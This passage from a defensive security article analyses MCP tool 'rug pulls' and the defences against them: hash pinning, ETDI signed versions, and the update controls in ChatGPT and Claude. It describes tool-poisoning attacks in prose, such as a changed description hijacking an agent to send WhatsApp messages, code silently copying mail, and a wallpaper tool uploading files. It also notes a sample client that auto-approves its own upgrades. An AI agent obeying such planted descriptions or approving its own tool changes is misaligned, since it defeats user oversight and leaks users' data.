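*We built the security layer MCP always needed* (2025), from the security firm Trail of Bits, describes mcp-context-protector, a wrapper that runs between client and server. The client launches it in place of the server, and it blocks everything until the user has reviewed and approved the server's instructions, tool descriptions and parameter descriptions in a separate command-line program. During the review, the wrapper makes visible any control characters that can hide text in a terminal. It then saves the approved configuration in a local database. If a tool later appears or changes, the wrapper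 withholds that tool from the client. If the server's general instructions change, it blocks the whole server, because those instructions could affect the use of any tool. Unlike ETDI, a proposal for signed tool definitions, the wrapper does not require the server's publisher to cooperate.

mcpseal also sits between client and server, but it keeps its hashes in a lock file stored with the project. When a definition changes, its `diff` command shows the old and new descriptions and `approve` accepts the current one. The `scan` command reports failure if anything has changed, so a team can run it automatically whenever someone proposes a change to the project.

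A shared lock file lets one developer review for the whole team, and every new approval appears in the project's history. But it also brings back part of the Cursor problem, because someone with write access to the repository could replace a hash in the lock file or edit the client's settings to launch the server directly. The team can guard against this by requiring a second person to approve edits to either file. An attacker who controls only the repository can't change a local database like the one in mcp-context-protector, but each user then has to do the review herself.

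### Tests of models and clients

Yang, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *MCPSECBENCH*, tested 17 kinds of attack on three platforms: Claude Desktop with Claude Opus 4.5, OpenAI's platform with GPT-4.1, and Cursor 2.3.29. They ran each attack 15 times on each platform. A run counted as a success if the attack made the system break one of the benchmark's security rules, as a refusal if the client or model detected the attack and declined, and as an error if it failed for an unrelated technical reason. A language model judged the outcomes.

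For post-approval change, the rule is that only verified tools may run. If *t* is the approved tool and an update adds a malicious modification *δ*, the result *t* + *δ* is a different tool, and the earlier verification no longer applies to it. Yang and colleagues ran this attack without added protection and then with each of two research defences, MCIP-Guardian and Firewalled-Agentic-Networks. These are the successful attacks out of 15, converted from the published percentages:

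| Protection | Claude Desktop | OpenAI | Cursor |
|---|---|---|---|
| None added | 14 | 11 | 14 |
| MCIP-Guardian | 0 | 12 | 15 |
| Firewalled-Agentic-Networks | 0 | 14 | 10 |

The zeros for Claude Desktop are less impressive than they look, since only nine of the 15 runs with Firewalled-Agentic-Networks ended in a refusal. Across all three platforms, Yang and colleagues credit MCIP-Guardian with stopping 4.4 per cent of these attacks, which would be two of 45 runs, and Firewalled-Agentic-Networks with stopping 13.3 per cent, which would be six. They attribute part of the rise in refusals to the models themselves. The increases on OpenAI's platform could easily be due to chance, with only 15 runs each.

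These figures don't show how well hash pinning works, because the benchmark covers defences that operate during a conversation and leaves out scanners such as mcp-scan. A model that refuses has judged the new text suspicious without a record of the old text to compare it with, so a more plausible rewording might well have succeeded more often than the ones in the test. The Cursor result is still informative because version 2.3.29 came out long after the July 2025 fix. It is what one would expect if the fix covers the settings file but not the server's descriptions.

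*SchemaCaps* comes closer to the question of which clients notice. It examined what happens when an approved tool starts to accept more input than before, as of 30 September 2026:

| Software | Result | Basis |
|---|---|---|
| MCP's TypeScript and Python kits | The new call goes through; an application learns of the change only if its developer wrote code to listen for it | Test and source code |
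| Vercel AI SDK | No warning by default; an optional function reports the change | Test and source code |
| VS Code | Earlier approvals remain valid because they depend on the tool's name | Source code |
| Claude Code | Reloads the list; permission rules match tool names | Documentation |
| Claude Desktop and Cursor | Undetermined | Documentation |
| mcp-scan 0.4.2 | No warning, because the hash covers only the description | Test and source code |

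None of the six products whose behaviour the study could determine prompted the user for approval again. VS Code and Claude Code tie a saved decision to the tool's name, much as Cursor before version 1.3 tied it to the server's name, so a decision about `create_event` applies to whatever the server now offers under that name.

*When Neither Side Confirms* (2026) examined 41 open-source agent programs and developer kits and found that 32 have no approval step for an ordinary MCP call by default. In those 32, a changed tool can run without any prompt unless the user has added a checking program.

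### Harmless edits and unchanged definitions

People who run servers object that most changes to a description are improvements. MCProspero's *RFC 001* (2026), written by a small server operator, explains that changing the wording alone changes how a model uses a tool, so rewording is an ordinary way to fix a tool that models misuse. The same post cites a study of 10,240 MCP servers in which about 13 per cent had significant mismatches between description and code. The descriptions on roughly 1,300 servers may therefore need correcting, and every correction would alert users who had pinned the old text.

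Trail of Bits concedes much of this about its own program. A vendor with a large service may update its MCP server every time the service changes, and users who face repeated prompts may overlook a malicious edit or turn the protection off. Trail of Bits recommends that a central security team review servers that change often.

Central review reduces the work. If a firm's 200 employees all use the same 20 servers, and each server changes twice a month, having every employee review every change produces 8,000 prompts a month, while a central reviewer would deal with 40. Sorting fields before hashing removes some pointless alarms, and a standard form could prevent others, such as Cursor's prompt for an added space. The rest of the work is harder to remove. MCProspero's point is also a reason for review, because if new wording can change what an agent does, someone has to read it to know that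 it is harmless.

The other objection is that the hash covers a tool's definition but not the code that runs. In postmark-mcp, for example, the definitions stayed the same while the code began copying mail. jkelly-dev1 writes that a matching pin "proves UNCHANGED. It never proves SAFE", and even "unchanged" applies only to the hashed content.

For a local server, the usual response is to pin the package as well as the tool definition. Only the package pin could have kept out the postmark-mcp release, but it would have missed the Invariant Labs server, which the definition pin would have caught. A signed package still needs inspection. *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (2026) notes that a signature identifies a release's publisher and covers any hidden routine or compromised dependency along with the rest of the code.

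A user can't pin the code of a hosted server and can only watch what it returns. *TrustShiftProbe* (2026) studies servers that behave faithfully during vetting but manipulate their responses later. Scanners that inspect definitions find nothing wrong with such servers. The study's proposed defence, SHIELD, learns what a server's responses look like during the early period and compares later responses with that pattern. This applies trust on first use to behaviour, but it is less exact than a hash. Legitimate responses vary from call to call, so the defence needs a limit on how much variation to accept.

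## ETDI: a proposal for signed tool versions and compulsory re-approval

A client can use a stored hash to detect that a tool definition has changed, but not to determine who changed it or whether the publisher meant to release a new version. The Enhanced Tool Definition Interface (ETDI) would add signatures and version numbers to provide that information. Bhatt, Narajala and Habler proposed it in June 2025 as an extension to MCP, to protect against impostor tools and tools that become malicious after approval. Unlike hash checking, ETDI requires publishers to take part.

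### What the provider signs

A tool's provider generates a pair of cryptographic keys. It signs the tool's definition with the private key, which it keeps secret, and clients check the signature with the public key. If anyone without the private key alters the definition, the check fails. For the calendar tool in the earlier example, the signed text might contain:

```
name:         list_events
version:      1.2.0
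description:  List events on the user's calendar.
input:        start date, end date
output:       list of events
permissions:  calendar:read
```

The permissions are often OAuth scopes, and the client shows them to the user for approval. Each signed version is final, so a provider has to issue and sign a new version to change the definition. Bhatt and colleagues are inconsistent about which changes require a new version. Their principles require one for any change to the definition, but their security analysis mentions only "security-relevant aspects" such as permissions and input formats. The stricter rule is safer, because Invariant Labs hijacked an agent by changing only a description.

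Verified identity is probably the best-supported part of the proposal. Anbiaee, Dadkhah and Ghorbani (2026), in *When Tool Names Are Not Identities*, connected five models to a legitimate server and an attacker's server at the same time. They tried twelve combinations of name, description and input format for the attacker's tool. The worst results came when the tool copied the legitimate name, described the same task and accepted the same input. GPT-5.4, Qwen3.7 Max and DeepSeek V3 often ran the attacker's tool, while Claude Sonnet 5 more often asked which one the user meant. The study did not test ETDI, but if a client hid tools without the expected company's signature, the model would not have to choose between the two tools. The client would still need a reliable way to match keys to companies. Bhatt and colleagues suggest shipping keys with the application, keeping them in a trusted registry,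 or using certificate authorities, as websites do.

### The approval procedure

The proposal includes simplified pseudo-code for the check that a client runs when it first encounters a tool or receives an update. If the user has already approved version 1.2.0 of `list_events`, the possible outcomes are as follows, with the first encounter added for completeness:

| What the client finds | What it asks the user | Result |
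|---|---|---|
| Invalid signature | Nothing | Rejects the tool |
| Valid signature, tool not seen before | Whether to approve the new tool | Accepts it if she agrees |
| Version 1.2.0, same hash | Nothing | Accepts the tool |
| Version 1.2.0, different hash | Whether to re-approve, since the content changed | Logs tampering, then accepts the tool if she agrees |
| Version 1.3.0 | Whether to approve the new version | Accepts it if she agrees |
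| Version 1.1.0 | Nothing | Logs a warning and accepts the tool |

If a tool's hash changes but its version number does not, the user gets an ordinary question and can click through it. This is surprisingly mild, because the signature has already passed, so someone with the provider's private key must have signed a second text as version 1.2.0, which the rules forbid. A stricter client could refuse the tool, since an honest provider can always reissue the text as 1.2.1.

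Older versions are handled worse, because the pseudo-code for them has only a comment that a policy should determine whether to "allow, warn, or block older versions". With no policy filled in, the client continues to the last step, records version 1.1.0 as approved and reports success. A server could use this to bring back a genuine old release with a known flaw. *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents* (2026) lists such rollbacks as a type of attack on MCP.

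Someone who holds the signing key could do more damage by writing a new definition that requests permission to delete events, labelling it 1.1.0 and signing it. The client compares hashes only when the version numbers match, so it would accept the new permission without asking anyone. Blocking every version below the approved one would close this gap. But users sometimes need to go back when an upgrade breaks something, so the client should still let them deliberately choose an earlier version.

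The pseudo-code stores the tool's identifier, version, hash and permissions, but not the approved text. A client built exactly this way could show that version 1.3.0 adds `calendar:write`, but not which sentence of the description is new.

### A wallpaper tool with new code

Bhatt and colleagues give the example of a tool called Daily Wallpaper that changes after the user approves it. Version 1.0 downloads a picture and sets it as the desktop background. The user lets it access the internet and change her wallpaper. Weeks later the provider, or someone who has broken into the server, alters the code so that it also searches her Documents folder for financial keywords and uploads the matching files. The version number stays at 1.0 to avoid a new approval.

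The published procedure would not stop this attack. Only the code has changed, so the server can keep sending the definition that the provider signed weeks ago. The signature is valid and the version and hash match the stored approval, so the client accepts the tool without prompting the user. ETDI would stop the attack only if the attacker also edited the definition, which he has no reason to do.

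The proposal partly addresses this by putting a hash of the tool's API contract into the signed definition. An API contract is a machine-readable document, often in the OpenAPI format, that lists the requests a service accepts and the form of its replies. Suppose the wallpaper service accepts one request, `GET /wallpaper/today`, and the provider adds another, `POST /documents`. The contract's hash changes, so the provider has to issue a new version and the user gets a prompt.

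However, malicious code can send the files to a different address without a new entry in the contract, while the wallpaper service still accepts the same single request. The provider also computes the contract hash itself, and in the pseudo-code the client never compares that hash with the running service, so a dishonest provider could change the interface and keep publishing the old hash. The claim that ETDI prevents post-approval changes therefore holds for changes to the signed definition and for interface changes that the provider reports, but not for new code behind the same interface.

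Some accounts of ETDI omit this limit. *Systematization of Knowledge* (Gaire, Gyawali and colleagues, 2025), a survey of MCP security, says that the scheme requires re-authorisation for "any functional change". The ETDI project's page, *ETDI Rug Poisoning Protection*, says more cautiously that the hash "ideally" covers the code as well. That is possible only for a local server, where the client can hash the installed package. It might work for Daily Wallpaper, since a program that searches the Documents folder must have some code on the user's machine.

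The project's design document, *Enhanced Tool Definition Interface (ETDI)*, includes a more ambitious diagram in which the client asks an identity provider, the service that issues OAuth tokens, to verify a tool's token "against actual behavior", and the identity provider reports a violation. But an identity provider normally handles token requests and cannot see which files a program opens. According to the accompanying text, the check works only if the client or the identity provider can compare the operation with the token's scopes.

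Later researchers have developed attacks that exploit this gap and defences against it. *Beyond Prompt Injection* (2026) describes an attack in which a malicious update keeps a tool's name, description and input format, so its code runs under the old approval. *ToolContractGate* (2026) presents a different checker of versioned definitions and acknowledges that a tool declared read-only can start writing records and still pass. *ProbeID* (2026) tries to detect such changes by testing a tool's responses and ignoring what the server reports about itself. That could expose a tool that starts giving different answers, but it could miss Daily Wallpaper, which would still deliver the right picture.

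### Hostile providers and stolen keys

Signing does not stop a hostile provider from changing a tool's code while leaving its definition alone, or from publishing a new version with a plausible explanation and waiting for users to approve it.

Signing would have prevented the postmark-mcp theft if clients had expected ActiveCampaign's key, because they would have rejected phanpak's copy at the first check, before anyone used it. If they had accepted phanpak's own key, ETDI would not have caught the harmful release, because version 1.0.16 did not change the tool definitions. At most, users would have seen a request to approve a new version with the same permissions.

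Anyone who steals an honest provider's private key can sign definitions that every client accepts as the provider's own. Bhatt and colleagues acknowledge that protection against impersonation depends on keeping this key secret. In their OAuth version of ETDI, the identity provider issues a signed token for each tool version, listing its scopes, and can limit the damage from a theft by revoking the token. According to the design document, revocation would disable the tool for everyone at once.

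Revocation helps only after someone has noticed the theft, and only if clients check for it. *Enhanced Tool Definition Interface (ETDI)* lets clients validate tokens with the identity provider's public keys alone. This is faster, but they won't learn of a revocation, because a revoked token's signature is still valid. Tokens that expire quickly reduce the problem. With one-hour tokens, a client could go on accepting a revoked tool for up to an hour. But the identity provider then has to be available all day to issue new tokens, and a mistake by the provider could disable a harmless tool for all its users.

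### Checking each call against a policy

In the proposal's second layer, the client or server describes the planned action before each call to a policy engine, a program that permits or denies requests according to written rules. This check does not depend on detecting changes. Bhatt and colleagues name two existing systems, Open Policy Agent and Amazon Verified Permissions. Two of the paper's three authors work at Amazon, though they state that the proposal is unrelated to their jobs.

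The request has four parts: the actor, the action, the resource and the context. In the proposal's example, version 1.2 of a vendor's tool requests access to read a private annual report for a user in a given department, at a given time and for a stated purpose. The engine can deny the call even though the user has approved the tool and its signature is valid.

In Invariant Labs' WhatsApp experiment, such a rule could have allowed messages only to the user's saved contacts. The planted description would still have misled the agent, but the rule would have blocked the call, provided the researchers' number was not a saved contact. It would have done so even if the user had approved the malicious description. It would also block some of the model's own mistakes with an unchanged tool, such as messaging a stranger.

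Policies can also reinforce version pins. The example identifies the tool as `ToolX_v1.2`, so an administrator can write a rule that permits only that version. If the engine denies anything the rules don't permit, version 1.3 cannot act until the administrator edits the rule, even if individual users have approved it.

In the proposal's pseudo-code, the engine checks a call before the client sends it. The engine would approve Daily Wallpaper's call to change the wallpaper. The altered code would then open the Documents folder directly, with the rights of the user's account and without another check by the engine. To stop the theft, a sandbox or some other barrier around the program has to apply the rules to every file it opens.

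Bhatt and colleagues recognise this requirement, writing that someone would have to certify or audit clients and servers to make sure every access to a resource goes through the engine. *ETDI Rug Poisoning Protection* is less careful when it says the framework will block altered code from exceeding its declared permissions. A mail service can refuse a request whose token lacks the right scope, but a program reading local files doesn't present a token to anyone.

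A barrier around the program can also miss data hidden in permitted traffic. In tests of 91 malicious tool variants, *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* found that a list of allowed destinations stopped all 71 that sent data to an attacker's host but none of the 20 that sent it to an allowed host. postmark-mcp leaked emails in a similar way, by sending blind copies through Postmark itself.

The proposal also includes rules on sequences of calls. An administrator could prevent a tool that reads a customer database from calling one that sends mail, or limit how often a tool may run. These rules suit tools that call each other, but the WhatsApp attack would not have triggered them because the agent never called the malicious tool.

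### Costs and missing measurements

Bhatt and colleagues acknowledge that ETDI adds work and delay. Providers have to protect signing keys and manage tokens, and administrators have to write policies and distribute them securely. Every token check adds some delay, and a call to a remote policy engine adds more. Bhatt and colleagues recommend caching keys and, where appropriate, policy decisions. But a client that reuses a cached decision will keep applying the old policy for a while after an administrator changes it.

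The number of prompts may be the hardest drawback to control. ETDI requires approval for each tool, not for the whole server. ActiveCampaign's server now has 24 tools, so a release that raised every tool's version number could produce 24 prompts unless the client grouped them. Bhatt and colleagues say designers must balance security with usability and cite research on how people respond to Android permission requests, but they did not test any prompts on users.

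One way to reduce the prompts is to ask only when an update gives the agent more power. *SchemaCaps*, which contrasts its approach with ETDI's on this point, requires a fresh decision only if a new input format accepts more than the old one. An update that removed an optional field would therefore not trigger a prompt. A changed description would still need its own check.

The proposal links to working code to show that it is feasible, but reports no measurements, such as attacks stopped, delay added or prompts shown. A separate system for signed definitions gives a rough idea of the delay. *Verifiable Manifest Signing and Transparency Enforcement for Secure MCP-Based LLM Pipelines* (2026) reports that verification took less than 5 milliseconds and that the system rejected more than 98 per cent of invalid requests. The injected attacks included replayed definitions, invalid signatures and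 hidden changes to metadata, all of which a signature system should catch. None involved changed code behind an intact definition, so the 98 per cent figure is weak evidence about an attack like Daily Wallpaper.

### Adoption by late 2026

ETDI has influenced research more than practice. Gaire and colleagues present it as a leading defence but add that checking a tool's origin does not limit what the tool can do. *Attested Tool-Server Admission* (2026) proposes a narrower extension to MCP that verifies a server's identity when it connects and leaves later changes to a separate monitor. This division has some appeal because a publisher would only have to prove its identity, and each client could choose its own rules for changes. The monitor would still need the verified identity, because otherwise an impostor could supply the definitions that the monitor treats as normal.

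MCP does not require re-approval, and its public registry lacks much of what ETDI would need. In *Same Name, Different Server*, Kraishan (2026) collected all 21,643 servers listed there in August 2026, with 72,606 version records. None of the records contained tool definitions, because the registry's format has no place for them. Signing was largely absent. Of the 8,900 servers with more than one version, 40.6 per cent had changed silently, meaning the listed identifiers stayed the same while something else, such as the description or the remote host, changed.

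Many of these changes were probably harmless rewording, but 370 servers had moved to a different host under the same name. ETDI as published would not necessarily flag such a move, because Bhatt and colleagues do not list the server's address among the contents of a signed definition. The new host could therefore present the old definition with its valid signature. Including the address in the signed text would fix this, but users would then see a prompt whenever a company changed its hosting.

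The only implementation found is the authors' own, *Model Context Protocol Python SDK with ETDI Security*. It is optional and works with ordinary MCP servers, so it can be adopted gradually, but many configurations still allow unsigned tools. It has three security levels. The description of the lowest, Basic, mentions signature checks, while detection of changed tools is first mentioned under the next level, Enhanced. Only Strict, the highest, blocks unverified tools. PyPI, the public registry for Python packages, has no provenance record for the current release, so users cannot check there how the package was built.

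The sample client on the same page also shows how easily a developer can bypass compulsory re-approval. It fetches the available tools, checks whether each one is verified, and calls `approve_tool` on every tool that passes, without asking a person. The sample is meant to demonstrate the functions, but a developer who copied it into a product would have an agent that approves its own upgrades.

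## ChatGPT workspaces: frozen tool lists and review of new actions

ETDI depends on publishers signing their tools, and hardly any do. OpenAI has built a simpler system for organisations that use ChatGPT, and it doesn't need the publisher's help. ChatGPT keeps a copy of the tool list an administrator approved and uses it until an administrator approves a newer one. This applies to only some ChatGPT integrations, and OpenAI changed the details more than once during 2026.

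A workspace is an organisation's shared ChatGPT account on a Business, Enterprise or Edu plan. OpenAI calls an integration an app and each of its tools an action. Since July 2026 it has listed apps inside plugins, which are packages that can also hold written instructions for particular tasks. How an app updates depends on its source. A custom app connects the workspace to an MCP server that the organisation chose, while a directory plugin comes from OpenAI's public list.

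### Custom apps keep the approved list

OpenAI's *Connecting custom MCP servers in ChatGPT* describes how to add custom apps to a workspace. An administrator enters the server's web address, ChatGPT fetches the tool definitions, and the administrator tests them privately before publishing the app. ChatGPT then works from a "frozen" snapshot of the tools and their inputs. If the server's developer later adds a tool called `delete_invoice`, nobody in the workspace can use it from that snapshot, and the administrator learns of it only by pressing Refresh, which fetches the current list. On Enterprise and Edu plans, new actions are switched off by default, and ChatGPT shows changes to existing actions as a diff, which marks the differences between the old and new definitions.

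This should stop the attack that Invariant Labs demonstrated, because ChatGPT keeps giving the model the approved description even after the server sends a different one. But the snapshot holds only the tool list. Calls still go to the live server, so an update that leaves the list unchanged, like the one to postmark-mcp, takes effect immediately.

Enterprise and Edu administrators can switch individual actions on or off, before and after publishing, and can limit an app to particular groups of members. Business administrators can also refresh the list, but OpenAI describes control over individual actions in custom apps only for Enterprise and Edu. Business customers had even less control at the start of the year. In *Incorrect UI path in Apps SDK docs*, a thread on OpenAI's forum, one participant quotes help-page instructions for them to recreate and republish an app whenever its tools changed.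 The customer who had asked then found a working Refresh button a few menus further down. Administrators would benefit from testing these controls as well as reading about them.

### Directory plugins update automatically

The rule for directory plugins used to be more like the rule for custom apps. In *How to surface mcp server updates for an existing plugin*, jbrodriguez asked why a small change to one tool's description had not appeared in ChatGPT. A respondent answered that OpenAI stored a reviewed snapshot of each published plugin, so the developer had to submit a new version and wait for approval. A respondent in *Questions About MCP Server Changes and ChatGPT App Re-submission* told developers to resubmit even if they had changed only the backend.

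OpenAI has since replaced this with what it calls continuous review. OpenAI scans each published server daily, and eligible changes go live once they pass automated checks, according to its *Upload and submit your plugin*. OpenAI's *Remote MCP server review requirements* gives the example of a notes service that adds `create_note`, lets `search` accept a folder and deletes `archive_note`. The next scan removes `archive_note` at once. If `create_note` passes the checks but the change to `search` does not, users get the new tool and keep the old definition of `search`. A developer who thinks the checks are wrong can appeal to OpenAI's review team.

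These checks protect against some bad updates, but OpenAI can't judge whether a particular company wants its agents to delete messages. For that, OpenAI's *Admin controls, security, and compliance for plugins and apps* describes a setting called "New actions", with three choices:

- Enable all new actions.
- Only enable new read actions.
- Disable new actions.

The last choice affects only actions added later. Some apps don't offer the setting, so the administrator can only allow or withhold the whole app. The setting was harder to reach in July 2026, when administrators saw the three choices only if they had first picked a custom set of actions for the app, according to OpenAI's *Kawalan pentadbir, keselamatan dan pematuhan untuk pemalam dan aplikasi*, a Malay edition of the same help page.

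| Kind of app | Plan | When a changed tool reaches members | What the administrator controls |
|---|---|---|---|
| Custom | Enterprise, Edu | After an administrator refreshes and publishes | Each action; new ones start switched off |
| Custom | Business | After an administrator refreshes and publishes | When to refresh; control of single actions is unclear |
| Directory plugin | All three | After OpenAI's automated checks | A rule for new actions, where the app supports it |

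The setting for directory plugins covers new actions, but OpenAI describes no equivalent for changes to the description or input format of an action that is already enabled. Even if an administrator has chosen "Disable new actions", `search` could start accepting a folder, or its description could gain an instruction to use it more often. OpenAI's *Connect and test your plugin* confirms that directory plugins and custom servers are treated differently, since it limits the manual refresh to custom servers. The plugins that most workspaces are likely to use are therefore controlled less strictly than the servers an organisation chose for itself.

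### What Anthropic documents for Claude connectors

Claude's controls apply mostly to tool calls and less to changes in the tool list. On Team and Enterprise plans, an organisation's owners can set each tool, or a whole category such as write and delete tools, to "Always allow", "Needs approval" or "Blocked", and members cannot override the choice. Enterprise customers can also set these levels by role, and the stricter of the role's and the organisation's levels applies. In Claude Cowork, Anthropic's product for longer office tasks, members have to approve write tools for each task unless an owner turns on a separate setting.

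Anthropic's *Set up role-based permissions on Enterprise plans* gives the example of a role that may search the issue tracker Jira, with approval, but may use none of Jira's other tools. Anthropic's documentation doesn't say what happens if Jira later adds a tool, such as `export_issues`, to a connector already in use. It does cover connectors that an owner adds later, which can inherit a baseline level for the role, but it doesn't mention a frozen list or a diff. A category set to "Blocked" may well block new write tools automatically, and an owner could check this by adding a tool to a test server. If the new tool falls under "Needs approval", members will see a prompt for each call, but the model will already have read the tool's description.

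### Comparing the approved list with the new one

Both companies leave the judgement about a changed integration to the customer. An administrator can make that judgement consistently by comparing two capability lists, the approved list A and the new list N. She matches tools by name, within a server that she identifies by its web address, and sorts them into three groups:

```
added:    tools in N but not in A
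removed:  tools in A but not in N
altered:  tools in both, with any difference in description,
          input format or labels
```

A renamed tool appears as one removal and one addition, which is the safe way to treat it. She then checks whether any tool in both lists has switched between reading and writing, and compares the OAuth scopes the integration requested before with those it requests now. She should also read the server's general instructions as part of the comparison.

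| Difference | New decision needed? | Why |
|---|---|---|
| Added tool that writes | Yes | The agent can do something new |
| Added tool that only reads | Yes, if it reaches new data or contacts outsiders | Reading can expose information |
| Removed tool | No | The agent can do less |
| New description or instructions | Yes, unless the change is plainly a correction | The wording affects when and how the model acts |
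| Input format accepts more | Yes | An approved tool can send or change more |
| Input format accepts less | No | The agent gains nothing, though old calls may fail |
| Tool relabelled from read to write | Yes | The earlier approval assumed that it changed nothing |
| Tool relabelled from write to read | Yes | The client may stop asking for confirmation |
| Added scope | Yes | The access token can do more |
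| Dropped scope | No | The access token can do less |

A change of label from write to read is easy to approve without scrutiny because it looks like a reduction in access. If the tool's code has not changed, the only effect is that the tool faces fewer checks. When a tool is removed, the administrator should delete its approval so that a later tool with the same name counts as new.

Slack's connector shows how the comparison works on a large change. PromptArmor's *Claude and ChatGPT Connectors Change Every 9 Minutes*, a study of connectors in both products in May and June 2026, found that Slack went from 14 tools to 32 and from 1 scope to 34. The arithmetic gives minimum figures:

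```
added tools − removed tools    = 32 − 14 = 18
added scopes − removed scopes  = 34 − 1  = 33
```

Slack therefore added at least 18 tools. If it removed none, all 14 approved tools are still there, and the administrator has to check each for altered text. If it removed or renamed three, it added 21 and only 11 remain to check. PromptArmor names four of the new powers: creating channels, inviting people, deleting messages and editing messages. All four are write actions, so each needs a new decision. Deleting a message also counts as destructive under OpenAI's definition, because it can't be undone. Inviting someone to a channel deserves similar caution, because an outsider may read its history, and that can't be undone either. If each power is one tool, at least 14 other new tools remain to classify.

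With "Enable all new actions", a workspace would receive all of these tools without a decision by its administrator. "Only enable new read actions" should block the four that write and allow any that search or list. "Disable new actions" would block all of them, leaving the agent with the tools it already had.

The administrator also has to decide on the new scopes, and needs to read what they permit to do so. The number of scopes is a poor measure of how much access grew, because one broad scope can permit more than a dozen narrow ones. The 14 Slack tools probably could not have worked with a single narrow permission, so the earlier list may have been incomplete, or Slack may have divided one broad permission into many narrow ones.

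### Scopes need a separate approval

OpenAI treats consent at the connected service and ChatGPT's action settings as separate checks. Approving a scope at Slack or Google does not enable a new action in ChatGPT, and disabling an action does not withdraw a scope. Different people may control the two. Microsoft's apps, for example, need permissions from an administrator of the company's Microsoft accounts, who may never have seen the ChatGPT settings.

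Microsoft's confirmation screen requires the approver to accept or refuse a permission request as a whole. To leave out a permission that enabled actions need, a ChatGPT administrator must first switch off every action that uses it, including those in other Microsoft apps covered by the same request. The review screen can also list permissions for "Upcoming" actions, which are not yet available. A company may therefore grant a permission long before the action that needs it exists, leaving only the decision in ChatGPT when the action arrives.

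### Tools that label themselves

The middle choice, "Only enable new read actions", is attractive because it lets harmless additions through, but it depends on read-only actions being correctly identified. That information starts with the server. When OpenAI scans a directory plugin, it imports the labels the developer attached to each tool. The `readOnlyHint` label should be true only if the tool retrieves data and changes nothing. Another label marks tools that can cause irreversible outcomes, and `openWorldHint` marks tools that reach the public internet or other outside parties.

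A developer must justify the labels when submitting a plugin, but OpenAI says these explanations don't override the labels. It lists mismatches between label and behaviour among the common reasons for rejecting a plugin. So a directory plugin's labels have had some outside scrutiny, though the developer can later change the server's code without changing the definition OpenAI checked. A custom app's labels have had less scrutiny, because OpenAI doesn't verify custom apps and makes the organisation responsible for vetting them.

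A false label could weaken two controls. Suppose a server labels `archive_channel` read-only, although it closes a Slack channel. If ChatGPT relies on that label, "Only enable new read actions" would switch the tool on. A separate permission, "Allow read actions", lets ChatGPT use read actions without asking the member, so the same label could also remove the confirmation prompt. ChatGPT may still ask or refuse because of the action's context, which gives some protection beyond the label. These permissions apply to ordinary conversations. For Workspace Agents, which members build to carry out set tasks, the builder decides which actions are available and when the agent must ask.

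An administrator can check a tool's label against its OAuth scopes. A tool labelled read-only that needs permission to manage channels deserves a closer look. She can also run the tool on a test account and see whether anything changed.

Even a tool correctly labelled as read-only can leak confidential data. OpenAI's definition of `openWorldHint` includes read-only tools such as web search, and an agent that can read confidential files and search the web can put a confidential sentence into a search query. The three choices for new actions don't depend on whether a tool contacts outsiders, so a company that handles sensitive data has good reason to choose "Disable new actions" and review the read tools too.

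### How often connectors change

The case for reviewing updates depends partly on how many there are. PromptArmor tracked 2,517 connectors in ChatGPT and Claude from mid-May to the end of June 2026 and found changes in 931 of them, or 37 per cent. It sells monitoring of such changes, so it benefits from a high count. The last column below scales its figures to a workspace with 20 average connectors.

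| Change | Count | Expected for 20 connectors in six weeks |
|---|---|---|
| Tools added | 1,686 | 13.4 |
| Tool descriptions rewritten | 1,127 | 9.0 |
| Tools with changed inputs | 664 | 5.3 |
| Connectors that began sending general instructions | 283 | 2.2 |
| OAuth scopes added | 86 | 0.7 |
| Connectors with a changed endpoint | 50 | 0.4 |
| Read-only connectors that gained write tools | 21 | 0.2 |
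| Tools relabelled from read to write | 12 | 0.1 |
| Connectors that gained a new way to display output | 8 | 0.1 |
| Total | 3,937 | 31.3 |

PromptArmor's headline figure is one change every nine minutes, which implies about 6,700 changes over six weeks. The itemised changes add up to only about 3,900, or one every 15 minutes. The headline figure may include kinds of change that the list leaves out, such as removed tools. The itemised total also counts some changes twice, because a read-only connector that gains a write tool has also added a tool. The smaller figure is the better basis for planning because readers can see what it includes.

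The 37 per cent is a share of 2,517 connectors that PromptArmor describes as already live, but its catalogue counts start at 1,442 and end at 2,468. Many of the 2,517 must therefore have joined during the study and had less time to change, so the share that changes in a full six weeks is probably higher.

After ChatGPT added a field for general instructions, 283 connectors began sending them, so this whole group of changes came from one decision by OpenAI rather than from vendors quietly expanding their own connectors. Some of these instructions still deserve attention. The data company Aleph's connector tells the model to call a feedback tool whenever results are wrong or incomplete, and PromptArmor points out that the feedback could contain sensitive data. The 12 tools that changed from read to write may have gained new powers, as PromptArmor assumes, or their developers may have corrected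 a wrong label.

Services gained new scopes much less often than new tools, and by PromptArmor's count, at least 57 of the 86 new scopes went to Slack, Dropbox and the expense service Brex. If consent were required only when permissions grow, as it is for browser extensions, users would not have been asked about most of the 1,686 new tools. Of the tools added in ChatGPT, 196 carried OpenAI's "destructive" label, and Google Drive alone went from 9 destructive tools to 16.

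### The review work for 20 connectors

At the average rate, an administrator with 20 connectors would have about 31 changes to review in six weeks, or five a week. If PromptArmor's headline rate is right, there would be 53, or nine a week. Assuming each review takes ten minutes, the work would take between 50 and 90 minutes a week. The changes would come in batches, because only about seven of the 20 connectors would change, and one afternoon with each of those seven might be enough.

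People tend to connect well-known services, though, and several of those change far more often than average. PromptArmor recorded 122 changes for Slack, 97 for GitHub, 87 for Dropbox, 70 for the project tracker Linear and 64 for the design tool Figma, a total of 440 across ChatGPT and Claude. If half of them occurred in the product that a workspace uses, its administrator would face 220 changes in six weeks, or about 37 a week. At ten minutes each, reviewing them would take about six hours a week, and she would soon start skimming. Large releases would make this worse. The security company Zscaler added 122 tools to its Claude connector in a single day.

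An administrator can reduce the number of decisions by setting new read actions to be allowed automatically. By the end of June, just under a third of ChatGPT's actions were write actions. If the new tools followed that pattern, about four of the 13 expected on 20 average connectors in six weeks would be write actions. She would have to decide only on those, provided the read and write labels were accurate. She would still have to check the nine rewritten descriptions. The diff would show them for a custom app, but for a directory plugin she would have to watch for them herself or pay a company such as PromptArmor to do so.

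These rates come from public catalogues and may not fit custom apps. A company that runs its own MCP server decides when the server changes, and its developers can tell the administrator before deploying a new version. The rates may also be out of date for ChatGPT's directory, because developers probably still had to submit each tool change as a new version in May and June. Continuous review has since made updates easier to publish.

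### When the frozen copy stops matching the server

OpenAI warns that calls can fail when the live server changes and no longer matches the frozen tool list. Old calls usually still work if the server adds an optional field, but if it renames a required one, ChatGPT keeps sending the old name and the server may reject every call. An administrator then has to refresh the list, review the change and publish it before the tool works again.

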